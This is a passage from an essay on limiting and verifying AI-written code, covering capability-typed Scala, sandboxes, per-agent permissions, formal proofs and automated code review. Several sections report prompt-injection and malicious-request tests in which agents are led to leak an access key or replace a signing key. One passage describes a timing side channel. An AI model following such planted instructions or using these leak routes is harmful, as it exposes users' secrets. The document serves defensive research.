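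A pure `compute` therefore cannot send data anywhere or store one customer's purchases for the next statement, which the interface of Statements alone did not rule out. A reviewer who wants to know where data goes can skip the module without trusting whoever wrote it.

### Using secret data without revealing it

Pure functions also let an agent work with data that it must not see. TACIT puts the contents of protected files in a wrapper called `Classified`. Its main operation, in simplified form, is:

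```
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

Here `T` and `U` stand for any types of data. The agent supplies a function `f`, and `map` applies it to the hidden data and wraps the result. For example, to count the customers who spent more than $1,000, an agent might write a function that takes the customer list and returns a number. If the agent prints the result, it sees only `Classified(****)`, while the user sees the number on a separate channel.

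Data could get out of `f` through an effect, such as a message, or through the return value. The compiler blocks effects by requiring `f` to be pure, and the wrapper hides the return value. In one test, an agent read a GitHub access key and tried to print it from inside `map`. Printing requires a capability, so the compiler rejected the program before it ran.

Errors are a third way for data to escape, because an error message can contain it. The compiler can't rule out errors, since dividing by zero or running out of memory can interrupt almost any code. TACIT instead catches errors while the program runs and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap like any others.

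Some tasks, such as summarizing a contract, need a language model to read the secret text. TACIT can send the wrapped text to a separate model that the user trusts, typically on the user's own machine, and that model's answer comes back wrapped. The cloud-hosted agent can then save the summary to a protected file without reading it.

### Six restrictions on agents' code

Ordinary Scala has features that let programmers override the type system. Any of them could make a capability disappear from a type, so TACIT compiles agents' code in a restricted "safe mode".

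| Restriction | What it prevents |
|---|---|
| No unchecked type casts or pattern matches | Treating a value as another type that doesn't list its capabilities |
| No features from the `caps.unsafe` module | Using Scala's own ways around capability tracking |
| No `@unchecked` annotations | Telling the compiler to skip a check |
| No runtime reflection | Looking up and calling operations by name while the program runs, out of the compiler's sight |
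| Capture checking and explicit nulls switched on, with all changes to data tracked | Using capabilities or changing data in ways the types don't show |
| Only global objects and functions that are themselves safe | Causing untracked effects through a library |

Library authors sometimes need the forbidden features. For example, a function might save time by privately storing earlier results, which changes data but has no effect its users can observe. The author can mark such code as safe, and the compiler then accepts it without checking. People have to review these exceptions, because a mistake in one could undo the guarantee for all the code that uses it.

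### Did it stop leaks?

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and classified documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections (instructions planted in text that an agent reads). They also made 11 openly malicious requests, some written as if by a system administrator. Two models attempted all the tasks and requests with and without the `Classified` wrapper.

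| Model | Attack | Leaks with the wrapper | Leaks without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Prompt injection | 0 of 120 | 0 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Malicious request | 0 of 11 | 2 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Prompt injection | 0 of 120 | 3 of 120 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Malicious request | 0 of 11 | 8 of 11 |

The wrapper didn't stop the models from doing ordinary work. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with the wrapper and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. The large difference for Sonnet may be an artefact, since without the wrapper it often ran out of time or turns, or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

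None of the 262 protected trials leaked, but the true leak rate could still be as high as about 1%. The argument from the type rules is a better reason to trust the wrapper, and the trials mainly check that the implementation follows those rules. The attacks targeted the models, so a tougher test would use someone who knows the compiler well and looks for a flaw in it.

The researchers also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, an existing set of prompt-injection tests covering banking, office work, chat and travel. With two other models, AgentDojo counted one injection as successful in 1,926 trials. In that trial, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews that included the attacker's recommendation of another hotel. This counted as a success because the other hotel's name appeared in the answer.

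### Scope as a set of permissions

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), from largely the same group as TACIT, extends this approach to programs that get code from a model while they are running. A programmer writes `agent(...)` with a description of the task where the program needs a result. When the program reaches that point, a model writes the code, and the compiler checks it as if a programmer had typed it there.

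The generated code can use only what is in scope, meaning the variables and functions available at that point. Its scope therefore acts as its set of permissions. Here is a simplified example:

```
def write_all(customers): List[Message] =
  agent("write this month's statements")

def send_all(messages, mailer) =
  agent("send each message to its address")
```

If the program passes `mailer` only to `send_all`, code that a model writes inside `write_all` cannot send mail, even if a customer's name contains an instruction to do so. A reviewer can see this without knowing what code the model will write.

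LACUNA also rejects faulty code as a whole. In one example, a program holds a balance of 100 and prompts a model for code that subtracts 50 and returns the new balance. The model writes code that subtracts 50 but then returns text instead of a number. The compiler rejects all of the code before it runs, so the balance is still 100. In a language that finds such errors only at run time, the balance would already have changed to 50.

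More attacks succeeded against LACUNA than against TACIT. On AgentDojo, 8 of 1,898 injections achieved their goal. Zhao and colleagues explain that an attacker can still get the model to misuse a capability that the task legitimately grants. The compiler enforces the scope that the programmer sets for each call, so the protection depends on the programmer granting no more than the call needs.

### What the checks cost

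Capture checking is an experimental feature, and models have been trained on little code that uses it. Both groups compared their systems with agents that call tools in the usual way. Most of the tasks came from τ²-bench, which simulates customer service.

| System | Task | Model | Solved with ordinary tool calls | Solved with checked code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT | Airline | DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% |
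| TACIT | Retail | DeepSeek V3.2 | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| TACIT | Airline | MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| TACIT | Retail | MiniMax M2.5 | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| TACIT | Software issues | MiniMax M2.5 | 43.3% | 41.7% |
| LACUNA | Airline | DeepSeek V4 Flash | 75.5% | 70.0% |
| LACUNA | Retail | DeepSeek V4 Flash | 80.9% | 58.8% |
| LACUNA | All four service domains | DeepSeek V4 Flash | 90.0% | 76.0% |

TACIT seems to hinder agents very little. Agents using it resolved 5 fewer of 300 software issues. They did better on customer service tasks, which Odersky and colleagues attribute to clearer data types and the compiler's error messages. At most 7.9% of the programs that agents wrote for these tasks needed another attempt.

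This model scored 14 points lower with LACUNA than with ordinary tool calls, a substantial gap, although Zhao and colleagues describe the overall result as "on par" with the ordinary agent. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the code the model wrote for retail tasks, and 89% of what a weaker model wrote for telecom tasks. The types may not be the main cause of the lower score, because with LACUNA a model also has to write the agent's control flow as well as its individual actions. Zhao and colleagues expect models with more training in this kind of code to do better.

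These experiments tested short programs that agents write to act. Even in the software tasks, the agents' patches were ordinary code outside the type system. The same compiler could check a complete application, as in the `compute` example, but neither study shows how well agents write large programs under these rules.

### What remains possible

As with any bound, code can stay within its permitted effects and still produce a wrong total or send one customer's statement to another.

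A hostile author could also misuse a permission that the code needs. Run has to hold the mail sender, so it could send every statement to a stranger. The programmer can reduce this risk by restricting the mail sender to addresses from the customer file, but the type system doesn't require this. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) describes a check with a similar gap. It verifies that a skill, a package of instructions and scripts for an agent, uses only the capabilities it declares, but a skill may declare more than it needs.

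The type system does not track every way information can leak. A function inside `map` could run quickly if one bit of a secret key is 0 and slowly if it is 1, and an agent could learn the bit by timing the call. At one bit per call, a 128-bit key would take 128 calls. Code may also start another program, such as the version-control tool Git, which runs outside the Scala checks. TACIT can limit which commands an agent starts, but not what those commands do.

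The guarantee also holds only if certain components, called the trusted base, are correct. For TACIT, these are the Scala compiler, the library that defines the capabilities, the software that runs the compiled code and, if the user has one, the trusted local model. The guarantee does not depend on anything the agent writes, even if the agent is actively hostile.

The reusable part of the library, which serves every agent that uses the system, is about 1,000 lines long, so a reviewer reading 200 lines an hour could finish it in five hours. Each kind of task also needs its own tool definitions, typically a few hundred lines. The compiler is far too large to review this way. Researchers have produced machine-checked proofs that the basic rules of capture checking are sound, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode still needs a similar argument.

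### Sandboxes and WebAssembly components

People can also limit a program from outside by running it in a process sandbox, which gives it access to only certain files, network addresses or system operations. Sandboxing works for programs in any language, including existing programs, whereas Odersky and colleagues say Scala 3 is the only production-ready language with capability tracking of this kind.

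A sandbox applies the same permissions to every part of a process. The customer program needs to read the customer file and send email, so a sandbox around the whole program has to allow both. Statements could then read the file and email it out without breaking any rule. Odersky and colleagues make the same point about an agent that reads a private document and sends it to a cloud model. Both steps are permitted, but passing data from one to the other causes the leak.

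WebAssembly, a portable format for compiled code, can isolate a smaller unit. A WebAssembly component can reach anything outside itself only through functions that the host program connects to it. If Statements were a component with no such functions, it could only receive a bill and return text. It could still keep one customer's purchases in memory between calls, unless the host started a fresh copy for each customer.

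### Permission rules for agents

Permission rules apply to an agent's tool calls rather than to a program. The agent's harness, the software that carries out its calls, checks each call against a list of these rules. Bouras and colleagues tested how precise such lists need to be. In their set-up, an orchestrating agent had other agents run the tests, repair the code and verify the repair. The researchers planted an instruction in the project, such as in a source comment or the test output, to take an action that the repair did not need.

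A planted instruction might tell the agent running the tests to replace a signing key in an ordinary source file. A list of forbidden actions would probably miss this, because repairs normally involve editing source files. Even a list written for this task has to let some agent edit them. CapScope, a research system, gives each agent its own permissions, so only the agent making the repair can edit the code. Before any agent reads the project's files, a model uses the user's request and the file names to predict which permissions the whole task will need.

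| Permissions | Planted action carried out | Repairs completed | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ambient authority | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 seconds |
| Fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 seconds |
| One list for the task, shared by all agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 seconds |
| Separate permissions for each agent (CapScope) | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 seconds |

The fixed list made almost no difference. Separate permissions stopped most attacks, and agents still made at least as many repairs as with the shared list. However, separate permissions more than doubled the average time compared with ambient authority, partly because agents kept retrying actions that CapScope had blocked. The tests used one model and five small Python projects, so the exact rates may not apply to other work.

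Permission rules have a serious gap when the agent writes code. An agent that is allowed to run the tests can cause any effect the tested code causes, and it may have written that code itself. Bouras and colleagues therefore say that their system still needs a sandbox. The rules also stop applying once the finished program runs without the agent.

The table compares these limits with the dependency rules described earlier, which control which files may import which.

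| Limit | Smallest thing it can restrict | What people have to trust | Does it hold against a hostile author? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dependency rules | An import | The checker and the author | No, because some effects need no import |
| Permission rules | A tool call by one agent | The harness and whoever sets the permissions | For the call itself, but not for code that a permitted command runs |
| Process sandbox | A process | The operating system or sandbox software, and its settings | Yes for access to resources, but not for data passing between permitted ones |
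| WebAssembly component | A component | The software that runs it and the functions it receives | Yes for access to resources, but it can misuse the functions it receives |
| Tracked capabilities | A function or a single value | The compiler, the capability library and the software that runs the code | Yes, except for misuse of granted capabilities and untracked channels such as timing |

A team whose customer program is in Python can't use Scala's types, but it can limit Statements in another way. It could run the module in a separate process with no access to the network or to any files except those Python needs, and start a new process for each customer. That would be somewhat slower, but would give nearly the same protection as a pure function. This approach is practical only because Statements is already a separate module that takes a bill and returns text. In the original 400-line function,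 the charging rules share variables with the code that sends the mail, so somebody would have to separate them first.

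## Can people check a specification and a proof instead of the code?

Limiting what Statements can access doesn't make its totals right. A machine-checked proof can show that code does what its specification says for every possible input. People who trust the checker don't have to read the code or the proof, but they do have to read the specification, because the proof doesn't show that the specification is right. Specifications can be much shorter than code, but people and AI models often get them wrong.

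### How a machine-checked proof works

For this kind of proof, the specification has to be a statement in formal logic, and the proof is a chain of small logical steps showing that the code meets it. A proof checker examines every step and rejects the proof if any step is invalid, so it doesn't matter whether a person or an AI wrote the proof. Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, argues that this makes proofs one of the best uses of language models. If a model produces nonsense, it does no harm, because the checker rejects it and the agent has to try again.

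A proof can cover every input because it reasons about the text of the code instead of running it. Here is the loop in Statements that adds up a customer's charges:

```
total = 0
for each purchase made in month:
    invariant: total = sum of the charges for the purchases so far
    total = total + charge(purchase)
ensures: total = sum of the charges for all purchases made in month
```

The invariant is a statement that holds before and after every round of the loop. The proof has three steps:

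1. Before the first purchase, the total is 0, which is the sum of no charges.
2. If the invariant holds before a purchase, adding that purchase's charge keeps it true.
3. When the loop ends, "the purchases so far" are all the purchases made in that month, so the final condition holds.

These steps apply equally to a customer with no purchases and one with a million. Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, can find much of a proof like this by itself. But according to Dafny's *The Cost of Bugs and of Verification* (2025), users often have to supply invariants and other hints, which takes knowledge of logic that most developers lack. Language models can now write many of these hints.

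An attempted proof can also expose a fault. Suppose someone tries to prove that the original 400-line function sends each statement to the email on the same line of the customer file. If that email is filled in, the program has just copied it into `address`, and the claim holds. If it is blank, the proof fails because `address` still has its old value, and the program sends one customer's statement to another.

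### Proving one module at a time

Contracts let people or agents divide a large proof into smaller ones. To prove something about Run, a verifier assumes that the other three modules keep their contracts, without looking inside them, and checks that Run meets the conditions for calling them. The table applies this to the three-line version of Run from the first section, using the contracts from the skeleton.

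| Call in Run | What the proof may assume afterwards | What it has to show first |
|---|---|---|
| `Records.customers()` | Each customer's name, email and purchases come from one record | Nothing |
| `Statements.compute(...)` | The text has the right total for the purchases it received | Nothing |
| `Mailer.send(...)` | Exactly one message went out, to the address given | The address is not blank |

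The proof fails at the last call because a customer's email may be blank and Run doesn't check for this before it calls Mailer. Once somebody adds the check, the proof succeeds.

Each of the other modules needs its own proof that it satisfies its contract. If an agent later rewrites Statements, only that module's proof has to change, as long as its contract stays the same. A contract must also state what its module doesn't change. If `compute` might change the customer's email, the verifier can't prove that the statement goes to the right person. A type that guarantees `compute` is pure rules this out without a separate proof.

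### A valid proof of the wrong thing

Suppose the specification for a sorting function has one condition:

```
ensures: for all positions i < j, output[i] <= output[j]
```

A function that always returns an empty list meets this specification. An empty list has no two positions to compare, so nothing in it is out of order, and a checker would accept the proof. The missing condition is:

```
ensures: every item occurs as often in the output as in the input
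```

If the condition required only that the same items occur in both lists, a function could drop repeats and still meet it. The table shows four possible outputs for the input [3, 1, 3].

| Output | In order | Same items | Same items, equally often |
|---|---|---|---|
| [] | Yes | No | No |
| [1, 3] | Yes | Yes | No |
| [3, 1, 3] | No | Yes | Yes |
| [1, 3, 3] | Yes | Yes | Yes |

If the items were purchases, the weaker condition would allow a program to charge a customer once for buying the same thing twice.

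Published theorems can leave similar gaps. A post on kirancodes.me quotes one of the main theorems for lean-zip, a compression program written and verified in the proof language Lean. In only four lines, the theorem guarantees that compressing any data smaller than a gigabyte and then decompressing the result gives back the original. That is useful, but on its own the theorem would also hold for a program whose compression and decompression steps both returned their input unchanged.

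A specification can also contain an assumption that nothing satisfies. *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) gives an example from a benchmark called FaithformBench. If 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 45. The benchmark gave an AI model a false version, with 51 in place of 45, to translate into Lean. The model declared x to be a natural number. No natural number makes 3^x equal 5, and in logic anything follows from an impossible assumption, so the false claim became provable.

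### From one kernel to 123 libraries

Until recently, proofs took too much work for most software. The standard example is seL4, a microkernel (the small central part of an operating system). According to *AI Could Make Formal Verification Economically Viable at Scale* (2025), verifying its 8,700 lines of C took 20 person-years and 200,000 lines of proof. Proofcraft (2026) extended that work in August 2026 by completing a proof that seL4 on AArch64, a widely used processor architecture, stops applications from learning information without authorization.

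In October 2026, Anthropic and the verification company Theorem reported a far larger set of proofs, in which Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries (Anthropic, *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale*, 2026). Theorem had already used AI to translate the 1,276 statements of a logic textbook from one proof language to another. The company says this took about two person-days, compared with an estimated 2.75 person-years by hand.

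The libraries came with fuzz tests, small programs that feed arbitrary bytes to part of a library. As OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) explains, the researchers automatically turned these tests into formal specifications, and Claude then had to prove a claim about all inputs up to a fixed size:

```
for every input under 64 MB:
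    the test program exits normally
```

EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) adds that the proofs cover 239 tests, and that a normal exit means no crash, memory error or failed assertion (a check written into the code). More than 2^500,000,000 inputs fall below the limit, so testing could not establish that the tests exit normally on all of them.

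The proofs are about machine instructions for RISC-V, an open processor design, so they don't depend on the compiler. A proof about source code may not apply to the compiled program if the compiler has a bug. Leip (2026), in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, gives the same reason for working on compiled programs for x86, which is harder to model than RISC-V but much more widely used.

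These proofs are too long for people to read. A program of 18,000 instructions needed about 600,000 lines in the proof language Rocq, or 33 lines per instruction. *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (OpenNET and Smith, 2026) puts the project's total at about 180 million lines, while *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (Keles, 2026) puts it at a billion. At 200 lines an hour, reading even 180 million lines would take one person about 450 working years.

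In November, Google DeepMind published *AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026), in which AI agents proved security properties of libsignal, the reference implementation of the protocol behind the Signal messaging app.

| | seL4 | Anthropic and Theorem | AlphaProof Code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code | A kernel of 8,700 lines of C | Compiled fuzz tests for 123 libraries | Signal's protocol library, as machine code |
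| Main result | The code does what its specification says for every input | The tests don't crash on any input under 64 MB | Four security properties, including a secret initial handshake |
| Lines of proof | 200,000 | About 180 million | About 6.5 million |
| Who wrote the proofs | Mostly people, over 20 person-years | Claude | AI agents |

The Anthropic project covers far more software than seL4, but for most of it the guarantee is much weaker. For example, an image library could return the wrong picture every time without ever crashing. The proofs also don't cover functions that the fuzz tests don't call. According to OpenNET, they leave out problems with multithreading (several parts of a program running at once), dynamic linking (loading shared code when a program starts) and faulty hardware. Compiling the same library for another processor produces a different program, which would need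 its own proof.

Claude proved more in a few cases, including that the Linux kernel's implementation of the zlib compression format follows the published standard. Trying to prove the libraries safe also uncovered hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed, including a memory error in the XML parser libexpat, and Claude prepared fixes.

### How well do models write specifications?

The fuzz tests gave Claude a ready-made specification, but most new programs don't have one. An agent that writes its own specification can repeat a misunderstanding there, as it can in its own tests.

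Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026), in *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*, tested how well agents write specifications and prove that code meets them. They used CLEVER, a benchmark of 161 small programming tasks in Lean. Each task has an English description and a human-written specification. The agent writes its own specification from the description and tries to prove it equivalent to the human one. It also writes the code and tries to prove that the code meets the human specification. In the benchmark's original evaluation, no system completed all these steps for more than one task.

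The three agents that Sosso and colleagues tested did much better, although newer models have since replaced all of them. But the agents also found mistakes in 80 of the 161 human-written specifications. CLEVER's creators reviewed and accepted all of these findings. An 81st task had a flawed supporting definition.

In 21 tasks, the specification misread the description. Most of the other mistakes were slips in writing the logic, and the most common of these was to write "and" where the author meant "if". In the customer program, that slip would look like this:

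```
wrong: for every customer, the email is not blank
       and exactly one message goes to it
right: for every customer, if the email is not blank,
       exactly one message goes to it
```

No program can meet the wrong version of the specification if the file contains a blank email. This error affected 15 tasks, and missing parentheses changed the meaning in another 12.

A flawed specification didn't always stop the agents from completing a proof:

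| Agent | Proved code against 78 sound specifications | Proved code against 81 flawed ones |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 70 | 34 |
| GPT-5.4 | 72 | 33 |
| Kimi K2.5 | 53 | 24 |

Each proof in the last column is valid, but it doesn't show that the code does what the English description asked for. The agents found the flaws more easily by comparing specifications. GPT-5.4 flagged 72 of the 81 flawed specifications when comparing them with versions it had written itself, but only 41 when trying to prove code against them. This supports the earlier suggestion that a second author should write the tests. A team could have two models write specifications independently and a person review the differences.

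The comparison can also fail. In two cases, Claude's proof that its specification was equivalent to the human one succeeded only because no program could meet either. Sosso and colleagues suggest catching this by requiring an example program that satisfies each specification.

On these small tasks, Claude wrote better specifications than the people had. In its first attempt, all 161 compiled and 147 (91.3%) passed the check as valid readings of the description. With short guidelines and example inputs, 157 passed. These validity judgements are the agent's own, though the researchers inspected them. Some descriptions have more than one reasonable reading, and no proof can settle which one is intended. For example, one task requires dates in the form mm-dd-yyyy but leaves unclear whether "3-5-2026" is acceptable.

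Larger or harder tasks give worse results. The table adds two findings that Tolmach and Klaus report from other studies.

| Task | Passes the automatic check | Faithful to the description or code |
|---|---|---|
| Small functions in Lean | 100% | 91.3% |
| Graduate-level mathematical statements in Lean | 89.5% | 60.5% |
| Models of real systems in the specification language TLA+ | Nearly 100% | About 46% |

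In *SWE-Proof*, 56% of Opus 4.8's specifications passed the audit, which fits this pattern. Tolmach and Klaus also describe a study of Verus, a tool for proving properties of Rust programs. The specifications that models wrote left out assumptions about inputs, accepted wrong outputs and rejected correct ones. Other AI models that judged these specifications missed a quarter of the failures.

Benchmark scores can hide this weakness. According to Sosso and colleagues, most benchmarks for verified code in Dafny, Verus and Lean supply the specification and test only the later steps. A high score on one of them shows that a model can write code and prove that it meets a given specification, but not that the model can write the specification itself.

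### Does the difficulty just move somewhere else?

Tolmach and Klaus, who work for the company Runtime Verification, argue that as proofs get easier to produce, the hard part becomes choosing the specification and the model, which is a mathematical description of the program or of the machine that runs it. Before anyone can prove that a queue shared by several threads is correct, somebody has to decide whether items must come out in order, whether the program can run out of memory, and which operations another thread can interrupt. The proof can be valid even if one of those decisions is wrong.

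Models of programs can contain errors that a checker can't detect. In one example, researchers asked Claude to describe how Etcd, a database, keeps its copies in agreement. Claude returned essentially the description from the appendix of the original research paper on the method Etcd uses. That description passed every check but had little to do with Etcd's code.

Proving properties of the machine code avoids this problem, because the proof is about the program that will run. Another approach is to test the model against the real program. Andrews and Zhang (2026), in *Formalizing CPython*, had agents translate functions from CPython, the standard program for running Python code, into Lean line by line. They ran each translation and the original on tens of thousands of inputs before trying to prove anything. A second agent then had to approve the work. So far 4,071 functions have passed, covering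 16% of CPython, and the proofs have led to 418 bug reports. Such tests can't prove that a translation is exact, but they would probably have exposed a model as inaccurate as the one of Etcd.

Even a careful specification can miss edge cases. Alongside the library proofs, Claude wrote an interpreter for part of Python and proved that it follows a formal specification of how CPython behaves. OpenNET reports that the interpreter and CPython gave the same result on 99.95% of more than 1.7 million random programs. They differed on the remaining 850 or so, all of which involved known edge cases.

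The remaining components that people have to trust can fail as well:

| What people trust | How it can fail | What they can do about it |
|---|---|---|
| The specification | It allows an empty list as a sorted one | Read it, try examples and compare it with a second version |
| The model of the program or machine | It describes a published method instead of the real code | Test it against the real program or processor |
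| Assumptions left unproved | One of them is false | Have the checker list them |
| The proof checker | It accepts an invalid proof | Run a separately written checker as well |
| Software and hardware outside the proof | A fault there corrupts a correct program | Test the finished system |

Lean allows an author to leave a step unproved by writing `sorry`, or to assume something without proof by declaring it an axiom. A reviewer therefore needs to look for both. Runtime Verification's *Verifying Linux's Rust Code* presents a proof that part of Binder, which lets Linux programs communicate, either returns a valid object or reports an error, whatever bytes it receives. The paper states that the proof leaves no steps unproved but relies on one axiom about the size of data in memory.

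Errors in the checker seem to be a smaller worry. Checkers are short programs, and Lean (2026) points out that when independent checkers give different results, the difference exposes bugs that one checker alone would miss.

The lean-zip post describes a test of what lies outside a proof, in which a Claude agent attacked the program over a weekend. In 105 million runs, the agent found no memory errors in the verified code. It did find one in Lean's runtime, the supporting software that every compiled Lean program uses. That error affected every version of Lean to date. The agent also found a denial-of-service fault, which could let an attacker make the program unavailable. Both bugs lay outside what the proofs covered, according to a passage quoted in jmason.ie's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* (2026). The proof held for the code it covered, but it would have been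 wrong to call the whole program verified.

### How much is left to read?

The usual reply to the objection is that specifications and machine models are short and reusable. The best measurement comes from AlphaProof Code, where people have to trust about 26,000 lines of specifications and machine model to rely on 6.5 million lines of proof. One person could read those 26,000 lines in 130 hours at 200 lines an hour, though dense logic may take longer than ordinary code. Many teams can reuse the part that describes AArch64 for other programs on the same kind of processor, so they can share the work of checking it.

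The ratio isn't always so good. Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It* describes a 2025 experiment in which Claude Code translated a research paper on concurrent programs into Lean. More than 60% of the result was definitions, which Lean can't check against the paper. The agent occasionally misunderstood a concept without causing any error, recorded the misunderstanding in comments, and later treated those comments as fact. Untangling these mistakes took expertise and so much time that the author thought the project had probably been slower than working by hand. Newer models may make fewer such mistakes, but somebody would still need to audit the definitions.

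The specification's length relative to the code also matters more to a reviewer than its length relative to the proof. The specification is often shorter than the code when the requirement is simple and the code is complicated. "Never crashes" takes one line for any library, and the two conditions for sorting stay the same however complicated the sorting method is. For the customer program, a few lines can specify that every statement must go to the customer whose purchases it lists.

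A full specification of the totals, however, has to define `charge(purchase)`, with every tax rate, discount and refund, because the invariant at the start of this section relies on it. Those rules take up much of the 220 lines in Statements, so their formal version could be nearly as long as the code. A proof would still catch mistakes in the code, such as a purchase counted twice. But someone who knows the charging rules would have to read their formal version closely, and may find it easier to check a few dozen worked examples.

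## Which parts of an AI-written program can go unread?

A module is a good candidate for going unread if it can affect very little, people can check its results without reading its code, and little else depends on it. Few modules meet all three conditions by chance, but a team can design a program so that more of them do. Firms that have reduced human review tend to use rougher methods, such as estimating the risk of each change. Their results are encouraging but hard to interpret.

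### Three conditions

Limits on what a module can do guard against harm that nobody thought to test for, such as the Statements module emailing the customer list to a stranger. Outside checks catch wrong results. If few other parts rely on the module, its mistakes don't spread far and the team can replace it easily. The table applies these conditions to the customer program.

| Module | What harm could it do? | Can people check its results from outside? | What depends on it? | Decision |
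|---|---|---|---|---|
| Records (120 lines) | Give one customer another's email | Mostly, by comparing its output with the file | Every later step | Read it |
| Statements (220 lines) | Charge the wrong amount, but nothing else if it has no access to mail, files or earlier customers | Yes, with worked examples from someone who knows the charging rules | Only Run | Leave it unread if something enforces the access limits |
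| Mailer (50 lines) | Send messages that nobody can take back | Partly, because the real mail service may behave differently from a stand-in | Only Run | Read it |
| Run (10 lines) | Send any customer's data to anyone | Yes, with a property-based test | Nothing | Read it, since this takes three minutes |

The reviewer still reads 180 lines, as in the first section, but the worked examples now cover the totals as well. A few examples could still miss a special rule for one customer. After an agent rewrites Statements, the team can run the old and new versions on last month's purchases and read only the statements that differ.

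In his 2025 talk *Vibe coding in prod*, the Anthropic researcher Erik Schluntz described a change that nearly met the conditions. Anthropic merged 22,000 lines, most of them written by Claude, into the code it uses for reinforcement learning (training a model by rewarding good results). Most of the change was in "leaf nodes", the parts of a program that nothing else depends on. The system ran entirely offline, so the engineers were confident that it posed no security problem. They designed inputs and outputs that people could easily verify, and ran long stress tests to check the system's stability. People spent days on the requirements and reviewed the parts they expected to extend later.

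Schluntz said the team ended up as confident in this change as in any other, but gave no figures on later faults. He also pointed out that outside checks can't measure technical debt, meaning shortcuts that make code harder to change. This debt matters less in a leaf node, which nobody is likely to build on.

### How firms decide what people read

Newman, Bird and colleagues interviewed 24 developers and surveyed 2,590 people at a large software company for *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices*. Of the 322 who answered a question about their role, 71% said their reviews had shifted towards higher-level concerns such as design and intent, and 14% disagreed. Some interviewees welcomed the shift because AI tools now deal with minor faults, but others had little choice. In the survey, 35% said that at least half the time they reviewed less thoroughly than they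 wanted to.

People who used AI for review reported slightly more difficulty keeping up with the volume of changes than people who didn't, perhaps because heavy workloads lead people to try the tools. Yet 78% of the AI users thought it had improved the quality of their reviews, and 68% thought it had made them faster.

Newman and colleagues also asked which other strategies helped most. These are the top five, along with a limit on the size of changes:

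| Strategy | Used it or saw it used | Chose it as one of the two most helpful |
|---|---|---|
| Authors review their own change, by hand or with AI, before submitting it | 41% | 27% |
| Authors explain the change's purpose and the decisions behind it | 36% | 26% |
| The team documents unwritten knowledge about the code | 40% | 19% |
| Managers encourage or reward review | 27% | 16% |
| Reviewers receive only finished changes | 41% | 15% |
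| A rule blocks changes that are too large or complex | 18% | 11% |

Most of these strategies make changes easier to review instead of letting anyone skip code. But reviewers do skip code. When asked how they had adapted, 57% said they now concentrate on selected parts of a change, and 36% said they assess its risk to decide how much attention it needs. These are opinions about what helps, and the study did not measure whether any strategy led people to find more faults.

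Meta lets some changes skip human review altogether. Adams, Banga and colleagues (2026), in *Automating Low-Risk Code Review at Meta*, report that lines of code per change rose by 105.9% in a year, while changes per developer rose by 51%, mostly because of AI agents. The share of changes that got a review within 24 hours fell, and some large groups had thousands waiting. Meta's answer is RADAR, a system that sorts changes in stages:

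| Stage | What happens |
|---|---|
| Source | RADAR separates changes by people, by AI agents and by scripts that make a fixed edit |
| Exclusions | Open-source code, code under US financial-reporting rules and code that needs extra reviews go to people |
| Risk score | A model predicts how likely the change is to cause a production incident (a failure in the live service), and only low-risk changes continue |
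| AI review | A language model reads the change and sends it to a person if it finds a risk, such as a logic error |
| Validation | Automatic checks run before the change is merged |

By default, a person's change qualifies only if its risk score is among the lowest 5%. For recurring tasks that agents carry out, the limit is 20%, or 50% for tasks with a strong safety record. A task must also have gone 60 days without causing an incident. Scripts that make the same mechanical edit everywhere can skip the later stages, because engineers approve the script once instead of checking each change.

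RADAR has reviewed over 535,000 changes and merged more than 331,000. The changes it reviewed were reverted a third as often as other changes and caused incidents one-fiftieth as often. But RADAR selects changes that were unlikely to cause trouble anyway, so these rates don't show that automated review is safer than human review. A fairer comparison would use equally low-risk changes that people had reviewed. Experts who examined the incidents apparently judged that a human reviewer would not have caught any of them.

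According to the paper, RADAR cut the median time to close a change by "over 330%", which is impossible. Engineering Enablement, a newsletter on developer productivity, interprets the figure as 3.3 times faster, or a reduction of about 70%.

A risk score predicts what a change will do but, unlike a sandbox or a type system, doesn't limit what the change can do. A small change to the layout of Statements could get a low score and still send the customer file somewhere.

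*From Code Review to Code Critique* (Maddila, Rashik and colleagues, 2026) describes a second system at Meta, which helps people decide where to look within a change. The system infers the purpose of the change from sources such as the developer's conversation with the agent, separately describes what the code does, and compares the two. If a developer asks for a new discount and the agent also alters how Records handles blank emails, the comparison should reveal the extra edit.

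The system also ranks the parts of a change that most need a person's attention. It did 2.4 times as well as Meta's existing AI reviewer on a measure of whether a change needs any comment. Such rankings could also narrow what people look at, as the AI's comments did in Tufano and colleagues' experiment.

Even *The End of Code Review*, which argues that most human review is now redundant, keeps people involved in architecture decisions with lasting consequences, security-critical code in regulated systems, and changes that depend on requirements no agent has seen. A charging rule that only the accountant knows would be one such requirement.

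### Two large code bases that agents wrote

Two accounts from February 2026 describe programs that agents wrote almost entirely, using models that are now old. *Building a C compiler with a team of parallel Claudes* (Carlini, 2026) covers an experiment at Anthropic with a C compiler, and *Harness engineering* (Lopopolo, 2026) covers an internal product at OpenAI that its Codex agents built.

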